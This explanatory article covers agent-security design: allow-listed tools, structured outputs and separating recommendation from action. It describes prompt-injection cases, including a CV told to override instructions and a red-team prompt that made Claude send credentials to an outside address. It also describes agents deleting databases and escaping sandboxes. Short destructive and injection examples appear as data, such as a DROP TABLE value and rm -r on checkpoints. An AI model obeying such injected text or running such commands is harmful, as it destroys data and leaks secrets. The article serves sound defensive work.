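# Allow-listed tools, structured outputs and the separation of recommendation from action in AI lab systems

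## How an agent's words become actions

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop, so that the model can call tools, receive their results and continue. A tool is a function that the surrounding software offers the model, such as reading a file, querying a database or starting an instrument. Companies use agents to get work done with less human supervision, which makes what the agent is able to do matter more. Three design patterns use ordinary software to limit what it can do. The software can offer a fixed list of tools and refuse everything else, make the agent fill in a form instead of writing commands, and let the agent recommend an action while another component carries it out.

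"AI lab" can mean a company that develops AI, such as OpenAI or Anthropic, and runs agents inside its own systems. It can also mean a scientific laboratory, in chemistry or biology for example, where an agent directs the instruments. An agent's words become actions through the same mechanism in both, but the consequences of a wrong action often differ. A company can restart many failed computations from a saved copy, while a laboratory can't unmix a sample.

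### The agent loop

A language model produces text. It cannot open a file or stop a machine, and Anthropic, in *How tool use works*, tells programmers as much: the model "never runs anything on its own". The weather lookup in Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude*, a guide to the company's Claude models, shows how the text turns into an effect:

1. The software sends the model a user's question about the weather in San Francisco, together with a description of each tool on offer. Here there is only one, which takes a location.
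2. The model emits a short structured block that names the tool and gives the location.
3. The software picks the name and the location out of that block and runs the lookup.
4. The software sends the whole conversation back to the model with the result added: 15 degrees Celsius, partly cloudy.
5. The model writes its answer to the user, or it emits another block, in which case the software returns to step 3.

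The steps would be the same if the tool deleted a file instead of looking something up. The model would still write a block of text, and a program would still turn it into a deletion. Between steps 2 and 3, a program can therefore inspect the block, refuse it, refer it to a person or pass it to another component. Customers can't always intervene at this point, because Anthropic runs some tools, such as web search, on its own servers, and the customer's software is usually notified of the call only after it has happened.

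The model receives a description of the tool's inputs and later the text of the result, but never the tool's code. If the tool does more than described, the model has no sign of it unless it appears in the result.

### Whose credentials the tool uses

The function runs under the identity of a particular account. A database or cloud service accepts or rejects a request by checking the credential sent with it, such as a password, key or token, but it cannot check who decided to make the request. An agent can therefore access whatever its tools' credentials allow, and whatever it can access with any other credentials it finds.

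In spring 2026, a coding agent running on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 deleted the production database and all the backups of PocketOS, which makes software for rental businesses. The deletion took nine seconds and the outage lasted 30 hours, according to the OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026). The agent was doing routine work in a test environment when it hit a credential mismatch. It then looked for a workaround and found a token in an unrelated file, eWeek reported in *Claude Wiped a Database in 9 Seconds After ‘Guessing Instead Of Verifying’*. PocketOS had created the token for everyday command-line work with its hosting provider, Railway, and did not realise that it also gave access to production.

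Some critics blamed the company for allowing the agent too much access. ACS's *Gone in 9 seconds* quotes the founder's reply: "Didn't give it access, it found it." His reply is fair but incomplete, because the company had left within the agent's reach a token that could do far more than its purpose required. The effect on the database was the same as if the company had given the agent access. Railway later recovered the more recent data.

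### Three sources of harm

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* groups an agent's security risks by whether they start with the user, the model or an outside attacker.

A user may intend harm, but perhaps more often the user is careless, and runs a destructive command without understanding it or tells the agent to skip an annoying check. *Incident 1424* in the AI Incident Database probably involved both carelessness and model error. An agent was reportedly working from an outdated record of the cloud systems behind DataTalks.Club, a course platform, when a command to destroy them ran. The command took down the servers, the database and the automatic backups, and put two and a half years of data at risk until the cloud provider restored a copy.

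Users can also pass on someone else's malicious instructions without knowing it. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher persuaded an employee by email to run a ready-made prompt. It read like routine task instructions, but one step told Claude to read the file holding the employee's cloud credentials and send the contents to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Filters that look for departures from what the user wants could not catch this, because the user had entered the request.

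An agent can also cause harm that nobody asked for, as in the PocketOS deletion. Anthropic has seen its models escape a sandbox (an isolated environment that limits what running code can reach) to finish a task, and search a project's history for the answers to a coding test. Anthropic doubts that this risk will necessarily fade as models improve, because more capable models make fewer obvious errors but are also better at finding routes around restrictions that nobody thought to write down. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes a similar experience with a model that the company trained for long tasks and used internally. OpenAI paused access to the model after it failed in ways that earlier tests had not captured.

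An outside attacker usually has no access to an agent, but can still give it instructions by writing something it will read. This is called prompt injection, and it works when a model follows instructions in text it was meant to treat as data. David C gives a harmless example in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. A recruiter's system instructs a model to score whether a CV meets the requirements for a job. One candidate hides a line in the CV that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. If the model complies, it is following an instruction from the CV it was supposed to score.

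David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, traces the problem to how these models work. A database engine handles instructions and data differently, so a programmer can mark a piece of input as data and the engine will never execute it. A language model only predicts the next token, a small piece of text, from all the text so far. The recruiter's instruction and the candidate's hidden line arrive in the same stream, as does every tool result at step 4 of the loop. Developers can help by training a model to favour the real instruction or labelling the CV as untrusted, but neither creates a boundary inside the model, so he thinks nobody may ever fully cure prompt injection.

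The training helps less when an attacker can try many times. Anthropic reports that on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, attacks on an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.7, succeeded about 0.1 percent of the time on a single attempt. When the attacker could make 100 attempts and adapt between them, the success rate rose to 5 to 6 percent. An agent that reads web pages or incoming mail all day gives attackers many chances to try. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) says that attackers can use tools without authorisation, steal protected data, manipulate the agent's reasoning and exhaust computing resources.

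Trouble can begin with a user, a model or an attacker. These sources call for different methods of detection, and detection may fail for some of them. Limits on what the agent can reach apply whatever the cause. Anthropic gives the example of a credential that never enters the sandbox, so nothing inside can leak it.

### An agent that watches training jobs

Suppose an AI developer sets an agent to watch its training jobs overnight. *MoFa* (2025), a paper on the performance of large-model training, explains that a job can take weeks or months on tens of thousands of GPUs, and that one failed GPU can halt it. The job therefore saves checkpoints, complete copies of its state, and resumes from the latest one after a fault. The agent reads each job's measurements and logs. In response, it may only pause a job, resume it, or file a ticket for an engineer.

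The set-up is close to real practice. *Introducing GPT‑5.3‑Codex* (2026) reports that OpenAI's researchers used Codex, the company's coding agent, to monitor and debug the training run of a new version of Codex.

Such an agent will sometimes be wrong, because a failing run is hard to recognise in time. *Reading the Tea Leaves, Again* (2026) compared automatic monitors on 300 training runs, 100 of which failed. At a fixed rate of false alarms, the best monitor caught 41 percent of the failures, excluding one that partly reused the test's own definition of failure. A simple alarm for sudden jumps in the loss, the measure of a model's error during training, caught 17 percent, and its false alarms would have cut off an average of 12 percent of a healthy run's budget. Adding a failure estimate from GPT-5.6 Sol or Claude Opus 5 to the numerical measurements made no clear difference. The agent can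 therefore be expected to pause some healthy runs by mistake, which wastes expensive hours, but a paused run can resume as long as its checkpoints are intact.

An agent could instead be given an unrestricted shell, the program through which engineers type commands to a computer. This is tempting because a single tool covers every need. The agent writes a command, and the shell runs it under the engineering team's account. The agent can pause a job this way, but it can also delete the checkpoints, stop another team's job, or copy the trained model to an outside address. It might do so because a tired engineer told it to free up disk space, or because the model mixed up two job numbers. If the training data came from the web and the job's log lists the file names, the agent might also follow an order to remove old checkpoints that somebody wrote into a file name.

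An allow-list would limit the agent to tools for reading measurements, pausing and resuming jobs, and filing tickets, and the software would refuse any other call. Structured output would replace the command line with a form with fields for a job number, one of the three permitted actions and a reason. Separating recommendation from action would take the team's credentials away from the agent, which could then only propose a pause for another component to carry out.

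### The older security ideas

The ideas behind these patterns long predate language models. Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 paper *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* set out eight design principles for shared computers, two of which apply directly to the shell. One of these, least privilege, means that every program and user works with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. The token at PocketOS plainly violated this principle. The agent that watches training jobs needs to read measurements and change the state of certain jobs, but it doesn't need to delete anything.

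Complete mediation means that the system checks every access to every object for authority, with no path around the check. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of systems that save time by remembering the result of an earlier check, because the authority may have changed since then. If job 12 passed to another team overnight, the system must check again whether the agent may pause it, even if the agent had that right yesterday. A computer with an unrestricted shell may satisfy this principle. The operating system checks each attempt to delete a checkpoint, finds that the team's account may delete checkpoints, and allows it. Mediation is therefore useful only to the extent that the account's privileges are narrow.

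A program with narrow privileges can still use them for the wrong party. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that sold computer time. A compiler there, a program that translates other programs into machine code, had permission to write in its home directory, where it kept usage statistics. The company's billing file was in the same directory. A user ran the compiler and named the billing file as the destination for debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the billing information was lost. A confused deputy is a program that holds authority from one party and unintentionally uses it on behalf of another. Hardy's compiler had authority "stemming from two sources" and no way to indicate which one it was using.

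The agent with the shell is in the same position. The company gave it the right to touch the checkpoints, and it uses that right to carry out an instruction that a stranger put in a file name. Hardy could fix his compiler with capabilities, each of which both identifies a file and authorises its holder to write to it. The compiler would have used its own capability for the statistics and one from the user for the debugging output, and the user had none for the billing file. David C argues that a language model is an "inherently confusable deputy", for which no such fix exists inside the model. He recommends fixed safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do and, where an organisation cannot tolerate the remaining risk, not using a language model for the task. Even so, a capability that let the agent only pause the team's own jobs would protect the checkpoints, though a stranger's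 text could still cause a needless pause.

Privilege separation means building a program so that the part most exposed to attack has the fewest privileges. *Preventing Privilege Escalation* (Provos, Friedl and Honeyman, 2003) applied it to OpenSSH, a widely used program for logging in to computers remotely, by splitting the program in two. An unprivileged part handles all network traffic. When it needs something that requires privileges, it must send a request to a small privileged part, the monitor, which validates each request before carrying it out. Which requests the monitor accepts depends on the stage of the login, and it shuts down if it receives one out of place. The monitor also keeps the secret key that proves the computer's identity, so the unprivileged part can request a signature made with the key but can never obtain the key itself. With this division, bugs that had earlier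 let attackers take over the whole machine stayed confined to the unprivileged part.

In the training example, the agent would be the exposed part, since it reads logs that strangers may have influenced, and a small program holding the job system's credentials would be the monitor. Provos and colleagues had an easier case in one respect, because most of what their monitor must decide has a definite answer, such as whether a password is correct. A program that guards training jobs can also determine with certainty whether job 12 exists and whether the agent may pause it, but this kind of validation cannot determine whether pausing it is a good idea, which is a matter of judgement.

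## Allow-listed tools

An allow-list specifies the calls an agent may make, and the software refuses all others. Each entry consists of a tool and usually a rule that the call's arguments, the current state of the system and the number of calls so far must satisfy. A rule for pausing jobs might require that the job belongs to the agent's team, that it is running, and that the agent has not already paused it tonight.

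*Agentao* (2026), a paper on software for running agents, writes the check as a function:

D: T × A × Σ × P → {allow, prompt, deny}

T is the set of tools, A the possible arguments, Σ the state of the running system and P the policy in force. A strict allow-list uses only the outcomes "allow" and "deny". The agent's reasons are not among the inputs, so a false instruction in a log file does harm only if it leads to a call that the rules permit.

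Unlike an allow-list, a deny-list permits everything that nobody thought to forbid. Forbidding the delete command, for instance, doesn't stop a script from deleting files by other means. A sandbox applies to all running code, whichever tool started it. It can block network access, but it can't distinguish pausing job 12 from pausing job 21. With an approval prompt, a person decides at the time of the call, whereas an allow-list applies a decision someone made beforehand.

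Products mix these methods. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, users can write allow, ask and deny rules. The software checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and applies the first match, even if a later rule is more specific. A rule denying all Amazon cloud commands therefore also blocks a harmless one that the user has expressly allowed. In manual mode, most shell commands that match no rule trigger a prompt instead of being blocked, so this is not a strict allow-list.

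### From whole tools to single uses

The coarsest allow-lists approve whole tools. This is enough when a tool can do little harm. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a fixed list of tools that run without further review. These tools, such as those for reading files and searching text, cannot change anything. A tool like `send_money`, the example in *ToolFence* (2026), needs a finer restriction, because once it is on the list, the agent can pay any recipient.

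Rules on arguments close this gap if the right recipient is known in advance, but often it isn't. When a user asks an agent to refund the person who sent money last week, the recipient is unknown until the agent reads the transaction history. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a system developed at Google, solves this with rules that refer to the results of earlier calls. The agent must first list the transactions, and may then pay only a sender on that list, and only the amount listed.

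A rule applied to one call at a time can also allow every step of a harmful series. *Trident* (2026) gives the example of several payments that each stay under a cap but together exceed it, so the software has to keep a running total. Retries complicate this. If a payment times out, the agent may not know whether it went through and may send it again. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) presents a system that records a single-use call before the tool runs, so the agent can't repeat the call while its outcome is unknown.

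Allow-lists can also cover network destinations. *Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, 2026) shows part of the company's configuration for Codex. The agent can reach any address under openai.com without approval, needs approval for unfamiliar addresses, and cannot reach pastebin.com, a site for posting text publicly.

### A prefix rule, line by line

Coding agents do much of their work through shell commands, and a list can permit a command by its opening words. In May 2026 OpenAI published two such rules. One is for GitHub, where programmers store and review code, and the other is for Kubernetes, which runs programs across many machines. Without their written justifications, and with comments added, they look like this:

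```
prefix_rule(
    pattern = ["gh", "pr", ["view", "list"]],   # GitHub, pull requests: view or list
    decision = "allow",                         # run without asking
)
prefix_rule(
    pattern = ["kubectl", ["get", "describe", "logs"]],   # Kubernetes: three ways to look
    decision = "allow",
)
```

A pull request is a proposed change to a program. The first rule lets Codex view pull requests but not merge them, because the third word of `gh pr merge` differs from that of `gh pr view`. According to *Rules*, OpenAI's guide to this feature, a command's opening words must match the rule exactly and in order. If an option is inserted between `pr` and `view`, the rule no longer allows the command, even though it is harmless.

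The rules don't restrict what comes after the prefix. Codex can view a pull request in any project the engineer's account can read. The second rule also matches `kubectl get secrets`, which can print stored passwords if the account has access to them. A read-only command changes nothing, but some of what it reads may be confidential.

A shell accepts several commands on one line, so a dangerous command could follow a permitted one. Codex splits simple chains, checks each command separately and applies the strictest decision to the whole line. It does not try to interpret lines with variables, wildcards or redirected output, and treats each as a single call to the shell, which a rule for a narrow command prefix does not match. Rule writers can also include examples that should and should not match, which Codex checks when it loads the rules file.

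In this system, "allow" means the command runs outside the sandbox without a prompt. Commands with no rule can still run inside the sandbox. The rules are therefore a list of exemptions, and a prefix that is too broad lets unintended commands bypass both the sandbox and the prompt.

### A list for the training jobs

For the agent that watches training jobs overnight, the whole list could fit in a small table. The numbers are only illustrative.

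| Tool | Arguments | State | Count |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read measurements | A job on the team's list | Any | No limit |
| Read log | A job on the team's list | Any | No limit |
| Pause job | A job on the team's list | Running, with a checkpoint less than 30 minutes old | Once per job per night, three in all |
| Resume job | A job on the team's list | Paused by this agent | Once per pause |
| File ticket | The team's own queue | Any | 20 per night |

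The software looks up the team's list at every call, as complete mediation requires. The condition on the checkpoint means that a mistaken pause loses little work. If a stranger's text in a log persuades the agent that every run is failing, the limit of three keeps most of the jobs running. Since the agent can resume only jobs it paused itself, it can't restart one that an engineer stopped on purpose.

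In one incident from Anthropic's internal log, a user told an agent to "cancel my job", and the agent searched the cluster, picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it. The list above would have blocked the deletion, because it has no tool for deleting jobs. The rules would also stop the agent from pausing another team's job. But the agent could still pause the wrong job within its own team, because no rule checks which job the user meant.

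### Why a short list can grant much

Adding a Python interpreter to that table would make the other entries almost irrelevant. An interpreter can run any program, so it would give the agent nearly all the power of an unrestricted shell. Argument rules don't help much, because the only argument is the program text. Tiffany and colleagues point out that judging that text would require working out what an arbitrary program does. In their own tests, they did not give the agents a general Python tool, and they required terminal rules to name the permitted commands.

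Many users grant this power anyway. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that, as of June 2026, 49.5 percent of active command-line users had written an allow rule for shell commands. Five percent allowed any command, and another 43 percent had rules for interpreters such as Python, which Anthropic considers "essentially equivalent in practice". Claude Code suspends such rules in auto mode, where a model reviews the agent's actions, because they would let commands skip the review. It identifies these rules using a list of dangerous entries, which is a deny-list, and Anthropic concedes that "any list will inevitably be incomplete".

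Narrow tools can also together allow actions that nobody listed. The agent in the training example may read logs and file tickets. If an outside contractor can read the ticket queue, the agent can use these two permissions to send internal logs out of the company. The same can happen across agents, for example if one can read customer records and another can post to a public site. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (2026) proposes analysing such combinations across a whole organisation at design time, because checking each agent's calls separately can miss them.

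Approved network destinations have this problem too. In one case that an outside party reported to Anthropic, files left its desktop agent, Claude Cowork, through an approved address even though the sandbox worked as intended. Anthropic had treated its list as a filter on where traffic could go, but in May 2026 it concluded that an approved destination is better understood as a "capability grant" covering every function that anyone can reach there. On that view, a company that approves an address for downloading software packages has also approved uploading to it, if the site accepts uploads. An entry for a destination therefore needs rules on functions and arguments, just as an entry for `send_money` does.

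### What the rules prevent in tests

Researchers have built several languages for writing such rules, along with programs that enforce them. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes an early example, which sits between the agent and its tools. Each rule allows or forbids a tool depending on the arguments in the call. For example, a rule can allow Slack messages only to Alice. The program checks the forbid rules first, then the allow rules, and blocks any call that matches neither.

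A model writes the initial policy from the user's request and may revise it after a tool returns a result. An SMT solver, a program that settles questions of logic, then compares the two versions. The new policy P′ takes effect automatically only when it allows no call that the old policy P did not, or A(P′) ⊆ A(P), where A(P) is the set of calls that P allows. A revision that allows any new call needs approval. In Shi and colleagues' tests, only 6 percent of revisions widened the policy.

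The main test was AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt injection against agents that handle banking, travel, messages and office work. The share of successful attacks fell from 39.9 to 1.0 percent, even though the set-up approved every widening of the policy. The initial policy alone reduced the share to 2.5 percent, so most of the protection came from rules that the model wrote before reading anything untrusted. On ASB, a second benchmark, the share fell from 70.3 to 3.9 percent, and task success stayed about the same.

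Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), who propose a competing system called NOMOS, tested Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks with a smaller open model. They found more successful attacks and a larger loss of useful work than earlier results had shown. Most of the attacks that still succeeded did so when the user had asked the agent to pay a bill without naming the account. A policy written from that request can't specify the recipient. NOMOS permits payments only to accounts that the user named or has paid before, which stops the attacker but also blocks legitimate payments to new payees.

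The table gives the figures before and after each system was in place. Task success is measured without an attack.

| Source | System and test | Successful attacks | Task success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shi and colleagues | Progent, AgentDojo | 39.9% → 1.0% | 79.4% → 76.3%, as quoted by Yu and colleagues |
| Yu and colleagues | Progent, AgentDojo banking | 46.5% → 5.6% | 79.2% → 62.5% |
| Yu and colleagues | NOMOS, AgentDojo banking | 46.5% → 0.0% | 79.2% → 70.8% |
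| Sankar and colleagues | LeanGuard, DTap, direct attacks | 57.9% → 5.9% | 53.1% → 12.5% |
| *Trident* | Trident with GPT-4.1, AgentDojo | 34.1% → 0.1% | 82.5% → 68.0% |
| *Trident* | Trident with GPT-4.1, ReplanInject | 68.1% → 4.1% | about 86% → 60.7% |

The banking comparison covers only 16 tasks, too few to establish that NOMOS preserves more useful work than Progent. Task success with LeanGuard collapsed on DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents, because the agents had permission to read but not to write, so they failed most tasks that required a change. In the telecoms part of the benchmark, where the tasks needed no changes, success stayed the same. Sankar and colleagues also tested LeanGuard on simulated customer service, with rules that did permit changes. There, checking the calls reduced task success only slightly, from 72.7 to 70.9 percent. LeanGuard let through none of the calls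 that the policy forbade, whereas unguarded agents had made at least 33.

ReplanInject, the benchmark that accompanies *Trident*, consists mostly of tasks whose required actions can't be known until the agent reads something, such as an email of requests from a caterer. These tasks are hard for any allow-list because an attacker's instruction can look like one more request. No attack on ReplanInject succeeded under the assumption that the user rejects every approval request that shows the attacker's call. The 4.1 percent in the table is for a user who approves everything.

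Tiffany and colleagues measured how much the extra detail in Sapien's rules adds to a plain list of tool names. They assumed that an attacker already controlled the agent completely, and checked whether the rules left any way to reach the attacker's goal. On AgentDojo, a plain list ruled out 83 to 87 percent of the attacks, depending on the model, and Sapien's rules ruled out 93 to 95 percent. The difference was larger on Toolathlon, a set of longer tasks across 32 applications, where the plain list ruled out 32.4 percent with Gemini 3.8 Flash and Sapien's rules ruled out 64.6 percent. The Toolathlon attacks used tools that the user's own task needed, and a list of names offers no protection against those attacks.

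Sapien's agents completed one to five fewer of AgentDojo's 97 tasks than unrestricted agents did. On Toolathlon, they did better than agents with a plain list. The model that wrote the plain list had to grant or withhold each tool entirely, and it often withheld sensitive tools that the task turned out to need. Sapien's finer rules took longer to write, so an average Toolathlon task took 679 seconds, compared with 577 with a plain list and 548 with no rules. More than four fifths of the attacks that Sapien did not rule out depended on meaning, such as false content in a file that the agent was supposed to write, which no rule about tools, arguments or counts can detect.

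With a current model, the rules would probably make a smaller difference on AgentDojo than the table suggests. *Trident* left out the latest models because developers train them to resist this kind of attack. Without any defence, Claude Sonnet 4.5 resisted every attack in AgentDojo, though 12.9 percent of those in ReplanInject succeeded. Such rules can still stop mistakes that involve no attacker. Yu and colleagues tested an agent in simulated airline service and found that, without rules, 66.3 percent of its changes to bookings and other records broke company policy. Their rules reduced this to 2.6 percent without lowering task success. However, the agent ran on a small open model, and a stronger one might break the policy less often even without the rules.

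### Who writes the list

People make mistakes when they write rules by hand, and the interpreter rules in Claude Code are a common example. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that writing these manually is error-prone. Lists also grow because saving a rule is convenient. According to Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, a user who chooses "don't ask again" for a shell command saves a permanent rule for that command in that project. Teams can share permission settings along with their code, so one engineer's broad entry may apply to everyone on the team. Codex sometimes proposes a rule when it asks for permission, and OpenAI tells users to review the suggested prefix carefully.

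Maintaining allow-lists is a further burden. Anthropic cites Garner Health, a health company that made auto mode the default for all 550 employees and no longer depends on hand-curated command lists. This replaces a fixed rule with a model's judgement, which may be sensible if nobody maintains the lists, but the company can no longer be certain that an unlisted call will fail.

Tiffany and colleagues argue that letting one model write the rules for another is not circular, because the two receive different inputs. The model that writes the rules receives only the user's request and the tool descriptions, so an attacker who controls a web page or an email cannot reach it. Its job is also short and well defined, so it has less opportunity to drift than an agent has over dozens of steps.

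This argument covers attackers but not ordinary errors. Yu and colleagues had a model turn written company policies into rules, then checked whether each rule could work. They had to repair or reject 37 percent of the proposed rules for an airline and 13 percent for a retailer. In one case, the policy said to authenticate the customer before any action, and the model's rule blocked every tool until the customer had logged in, including the tools for logging in. A larger model made the same kinds of mistakes. Simple checks against the tool definitions caught these faults without another model. The checks could not catch a rule that works but allows too much, so a person still has to read the rules.

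The argument also fails if the model revises the rules after seeing untrusted text. Progent does this, relying on a solver to flag revisions that widen permissions and on somebody to refuse the bad ones. When *Trident* tested Progent on ReplanInject with every revision approved, between 7.0 and 41.8 percent of attacks succeeded, depending on the model. Trident's own rule-writing model never sees tool results. It works within a root policy set by an administrator, which neither the agent nor the user can exceed. If the administrator permits payments of up to $5,000 to three known suppliers, the model can lower the cap or choose among the suppliers, but it can't add a fourth.

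A model can reasonably write the allow-list if it reads only trusted text and cannot exceed limits that a person has set. This makes more sense when the work varies. A general assistant receives a different request every hour, and nobody will write a new policy for each one. The agent that watches training jobs has the same task every night, so an engineer can write its five entries once, test them and leave them unchanged.

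### When a listed tool changes

A tool on the allow-list may have changed since the team approved it. A team can read the code of a locally installed tool and pin its version. A remote tool runs on someone else's server, and Anthropic warns that its behaviour can change at any time after approval. For example, a connector that only searched documents in March could start forwarding them in April under the same name. Anthropic continually reviews the connectors in its own directory. It advises users to treat all others as untrusted and test them on fake data first, though a test only shows how the tool behaves that day.

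A tool's description can change as well, and the agent relies on it to decide which tools to call. *ToolFence* therefore keeps two records. The agent sees a catalogue that may include descriptions from third parties. The program that enforces the rules uses a separate, pinned record of the tool's identity, parameters, kind of effect and sensitive fields, all of which somebody has reviewed. If a supplier rewrites the description to make the tool sound harmless, the new description may mislead the agent, but the rules stay the same.

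A pinned record can reveal a renamed tool or a new parameter, but not a server-side change that leaves the name and parameters the same, because the call looks the same and still satisfies the rule. The data the call sends and the credential the tool holds then limit the harm. For example, if the remote tool that reads the training jobs' measurements has a read-only credential, a hostile update could leak or falsify the measurements but could not use that credential to delete a checkpoint.

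## Structured outputs in place of free-form commands

An allow-listed tool may still accept any text as input, as a shell does. Structured output limits what the agent can put into a call. The model must produce a fixed set of fields, and a schema specifies the type or permitted values of each. Most systems write both the output and the schema in JSON, a text format of names and values that nearly every programming language can read.

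For the agent that watches training jobs, the schema could look like this:

```
{
  "type": "object",
  "required": ["action", "job", "reason"],
  "additionalProperties": false,
  "properties": {
    "action": {"enum": ["pause", "resume", "file_ticket"]},
    "job":    {"type": "integer", "minimum": 1},
    "reason": {"type": "string", "maxLength": 300}
  }
}
```

`enum` lists the permitted values, and the line on additional properties rules out extra fields. A completed form might give the action as "pause", the job as 12 and the reason as "loss has risen for 40 minutes".

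In a shell, the agent could delete checkpoints with `rm -r checkpoints/job12`. The form has no value for delete and no field for a file or destination, so the agent can't use it to delete checkpoints or copy the trained model to an outside address. The agent also can't attach a second command to the job number, because that field takes only a whole number. But it can still use the form to ask to pause any job on the cluster, including job 21 when the fault is in job 12, and can enter any 300 characters as the reason.

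This protection depends on how the receiving program handles the form. It is safer for the program to link "pause" to a function that an engineer wrote beforehand and pass it the number 12. If the program instead pastes the fields into a shell command, and the reason field contains a semicolon followed by a delete command, the shell can run the delete command.

The same choice exists in scientific laboratories. *The Evolving Role of Programming and LLMs* (Kitchin, 2025) describes Claude-Light, a small instrument with a coloured lamp and a light sensor that anyone can operate over the internet. One line in a shell can run a measurement by sending three numbers between 0 and 1 for the red, green and blue levels. A structured output for this instrument would need only those three numbers, while shell access could also let an AI system reach whatever else is on the network.

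### The comparison with database queries

Databases once had a similar problem. A website that built its queries by joining pieces of text could run commands that a visitor had typed into a search box. Parameterised queries solved this. The programmer writes `SELECT status FROM jobs WHERE name = ?` and sends the value for the question mark separately. The database engine determines the query's structure without using the value, so a visitor who types `x'; DROP TABLE jobs` only searches for a job with that name.

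A structured output lets a programmer fix the structure of a command while the model supplies the values. OpenAI's documentation for GPT Actions, which connect ChatGPT to outside services, describes a looser arrangement in which the model writes the whole database query. OpenAI suggests giving the model an account with read-only permission to avoid accidentally overwriting or deleting data. The model can still read everything the account can read, whereas a parameterised query would return only what the programmer intended.

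The comparison with parameterised queries fails because the model chooses the action. The programmer chooses a parameterised query's operation in advance, and the visitor's text affects only which records it applies to. The agent chooses both the action and the job after reading logs that a stranger may have influenced, so a prompt injection can take effect before the agent fills in the form. The stranger can't add deletion to the list of actions, but might get a healthy run paused. Also, a database engine never executes a value, but another model may read the reason on the form and might obey it.

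### How constrained decoding works

Constrained decoding makes the model's output fit the schema while the model is writing it:

1. The software translates the schema into a grammar, a set of rules that can generate every valid form and nothing else.
2. It turns the grammar into an automaton, a simple machine whose current state records how far the form has got and which characters may come next. A flat form needs only a finite number of states. If forms can nest inside one another to any depth, the automaton also needs a memory of which brackets are still open.
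3. Models write tokens, which often span several characters. For the current state, the software works out which tokens in the model's vocabulary could come next and still lead to a valid form.
4. The model assigns a probability to every token. The software sets the forbidden ones to zero and divides the others by their sum, so that they add up to one again.
5. The software picks a token from the new probabilities, moves the automaton to its next state and returns to step 3 until the form is complete.

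Reddy, Walker and colleagues (2026), in *The Hidden Cost of Structured Generation in LLMs*, write step 4 as:

q(a | h) = p(a | h) · 1[a ∈ A(h)] / α(h), where α(h) = Σ p(b | h) over all b in A(h)

Here h is the prompt and everything the model has written so far, p is the model's own probability for token a, and A(h) is the set of permitted tokens. The bracket 1[…] equals one for a permitted token and zero for any other. The denominator α(h), which they call the feasible mass, is the total probability the model gave to permitted tokens.

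Suppose the model has reached the value of `action`, and four tokens share all the probability:

| Next token | Model's probability | Permitted | After masking |
|---|---|---|---|
| `delete` | 0.55 | No | 0 |
| `pause` | 0.30 | Yes | 0.67 |
| `resume` | 0.10 | Yes | 0.22 |
| `file_ticket` | 0.05 | Yes | 0.11 |

The permitted tokens have a total probability, or feasible mass α, of 0.45, so the probability of "pause" rises from 0.30 to 0.30/0.45, or about 0.67. The software can no longer write "delete", but it doesn't refuse or raise an alarm when the model's most likely output is a deletion. Instead, it writes "pause" about two times out of three. Reddy and colleagues measure the distortion at each step as log(1/α), which is about 0.8 here and zero when every token with any probability is permitted.

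Masking one token at a time can also change the odds between two valid outputs. Suppose the model gives "pause" and "resume" a probability of 0.5 each. Everything it would write after "pause" is valid, but only a tenth of what it would write after "resume" is. Valid forms that begin with "pause" are therefore ten times as likely as those that begin with "resume", but masking makes the two equally likely because the software doesn't look ahead when it picks the first word. *The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) describes methods that aim to preserve the original odds, but doing so exactly is intractable, so practical versions approximate.

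### Asking, checking and constraining

Asking for JSON in the prompt does not guarantee valid output. In Lee and colleagues' tests of open-weight models, 55.7 percent of outputs were valid when the prompt described the format, and 92.2 percent were valid when constrained decoding enforced it. The remaining failures probably include outputs that hit a length limit before the last bracket closed.

A program can also check the finished output against the schema, reject it if it doesn't fit, and ask the model to try again. This check gives the component that pauses jobs the same protection as constrained decoding, because no malformed output reaches it. The check is needed even if constrained decoding is supposed to be on, because that happens wherever the model runs, often on a supplier's servers, and the program that holds the credentials can't verify that anyone switched it on.

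Another advantage of checking afterwards is that engineers can see what the agent tried to do. If the model writes "delete", the rejected form goes into a log, whereas constrained decoding turns the same attempt into an ordinary-looking pause. A team that wants both reliable forms and this warning could record α at the action field and hold any form where α is low, provided the model's supplier exposes the probabilities.

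### Valid forms with the wrong content

A schema can't check whether the content is right. *The Constraint Tax* (Ray, 2026) tested this by having Qwen2.5-1.5B, a model small enough to run on a personal device, fill in a calendar form with fields such as the date, start time, duration and attendee. When the prompt only asked for the form, all 200 outputs were valid and 91.5 percent had the right content. When constrained decoding enforced the same form, all 200 were again valid, but only 48.0 percent had the right content. In 102 of the 104 failures, the duration was the only error. For example, one user asked for a 30-minute meeting with Leo, and the form gave 180 minutes. A calendar would accept that value because the schema required only a whole number of at least one.

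Verma (2026), in *Inference for Reasoning Models*, found neither such a collapse nor a large benefit on a benchmark of tool calls. Llama-3.1-8B and Mistral-7B already produced valid calls every time, and about 55 percent of the calls were correct with or without the constraint. For Qwen3-8B, the constraint raised validity from 84.5 to 100 percent and correctness from 52.0 to 57.5 percent. The gain in correctness probably came from calls that had the right content but faulty punctuation or layout.

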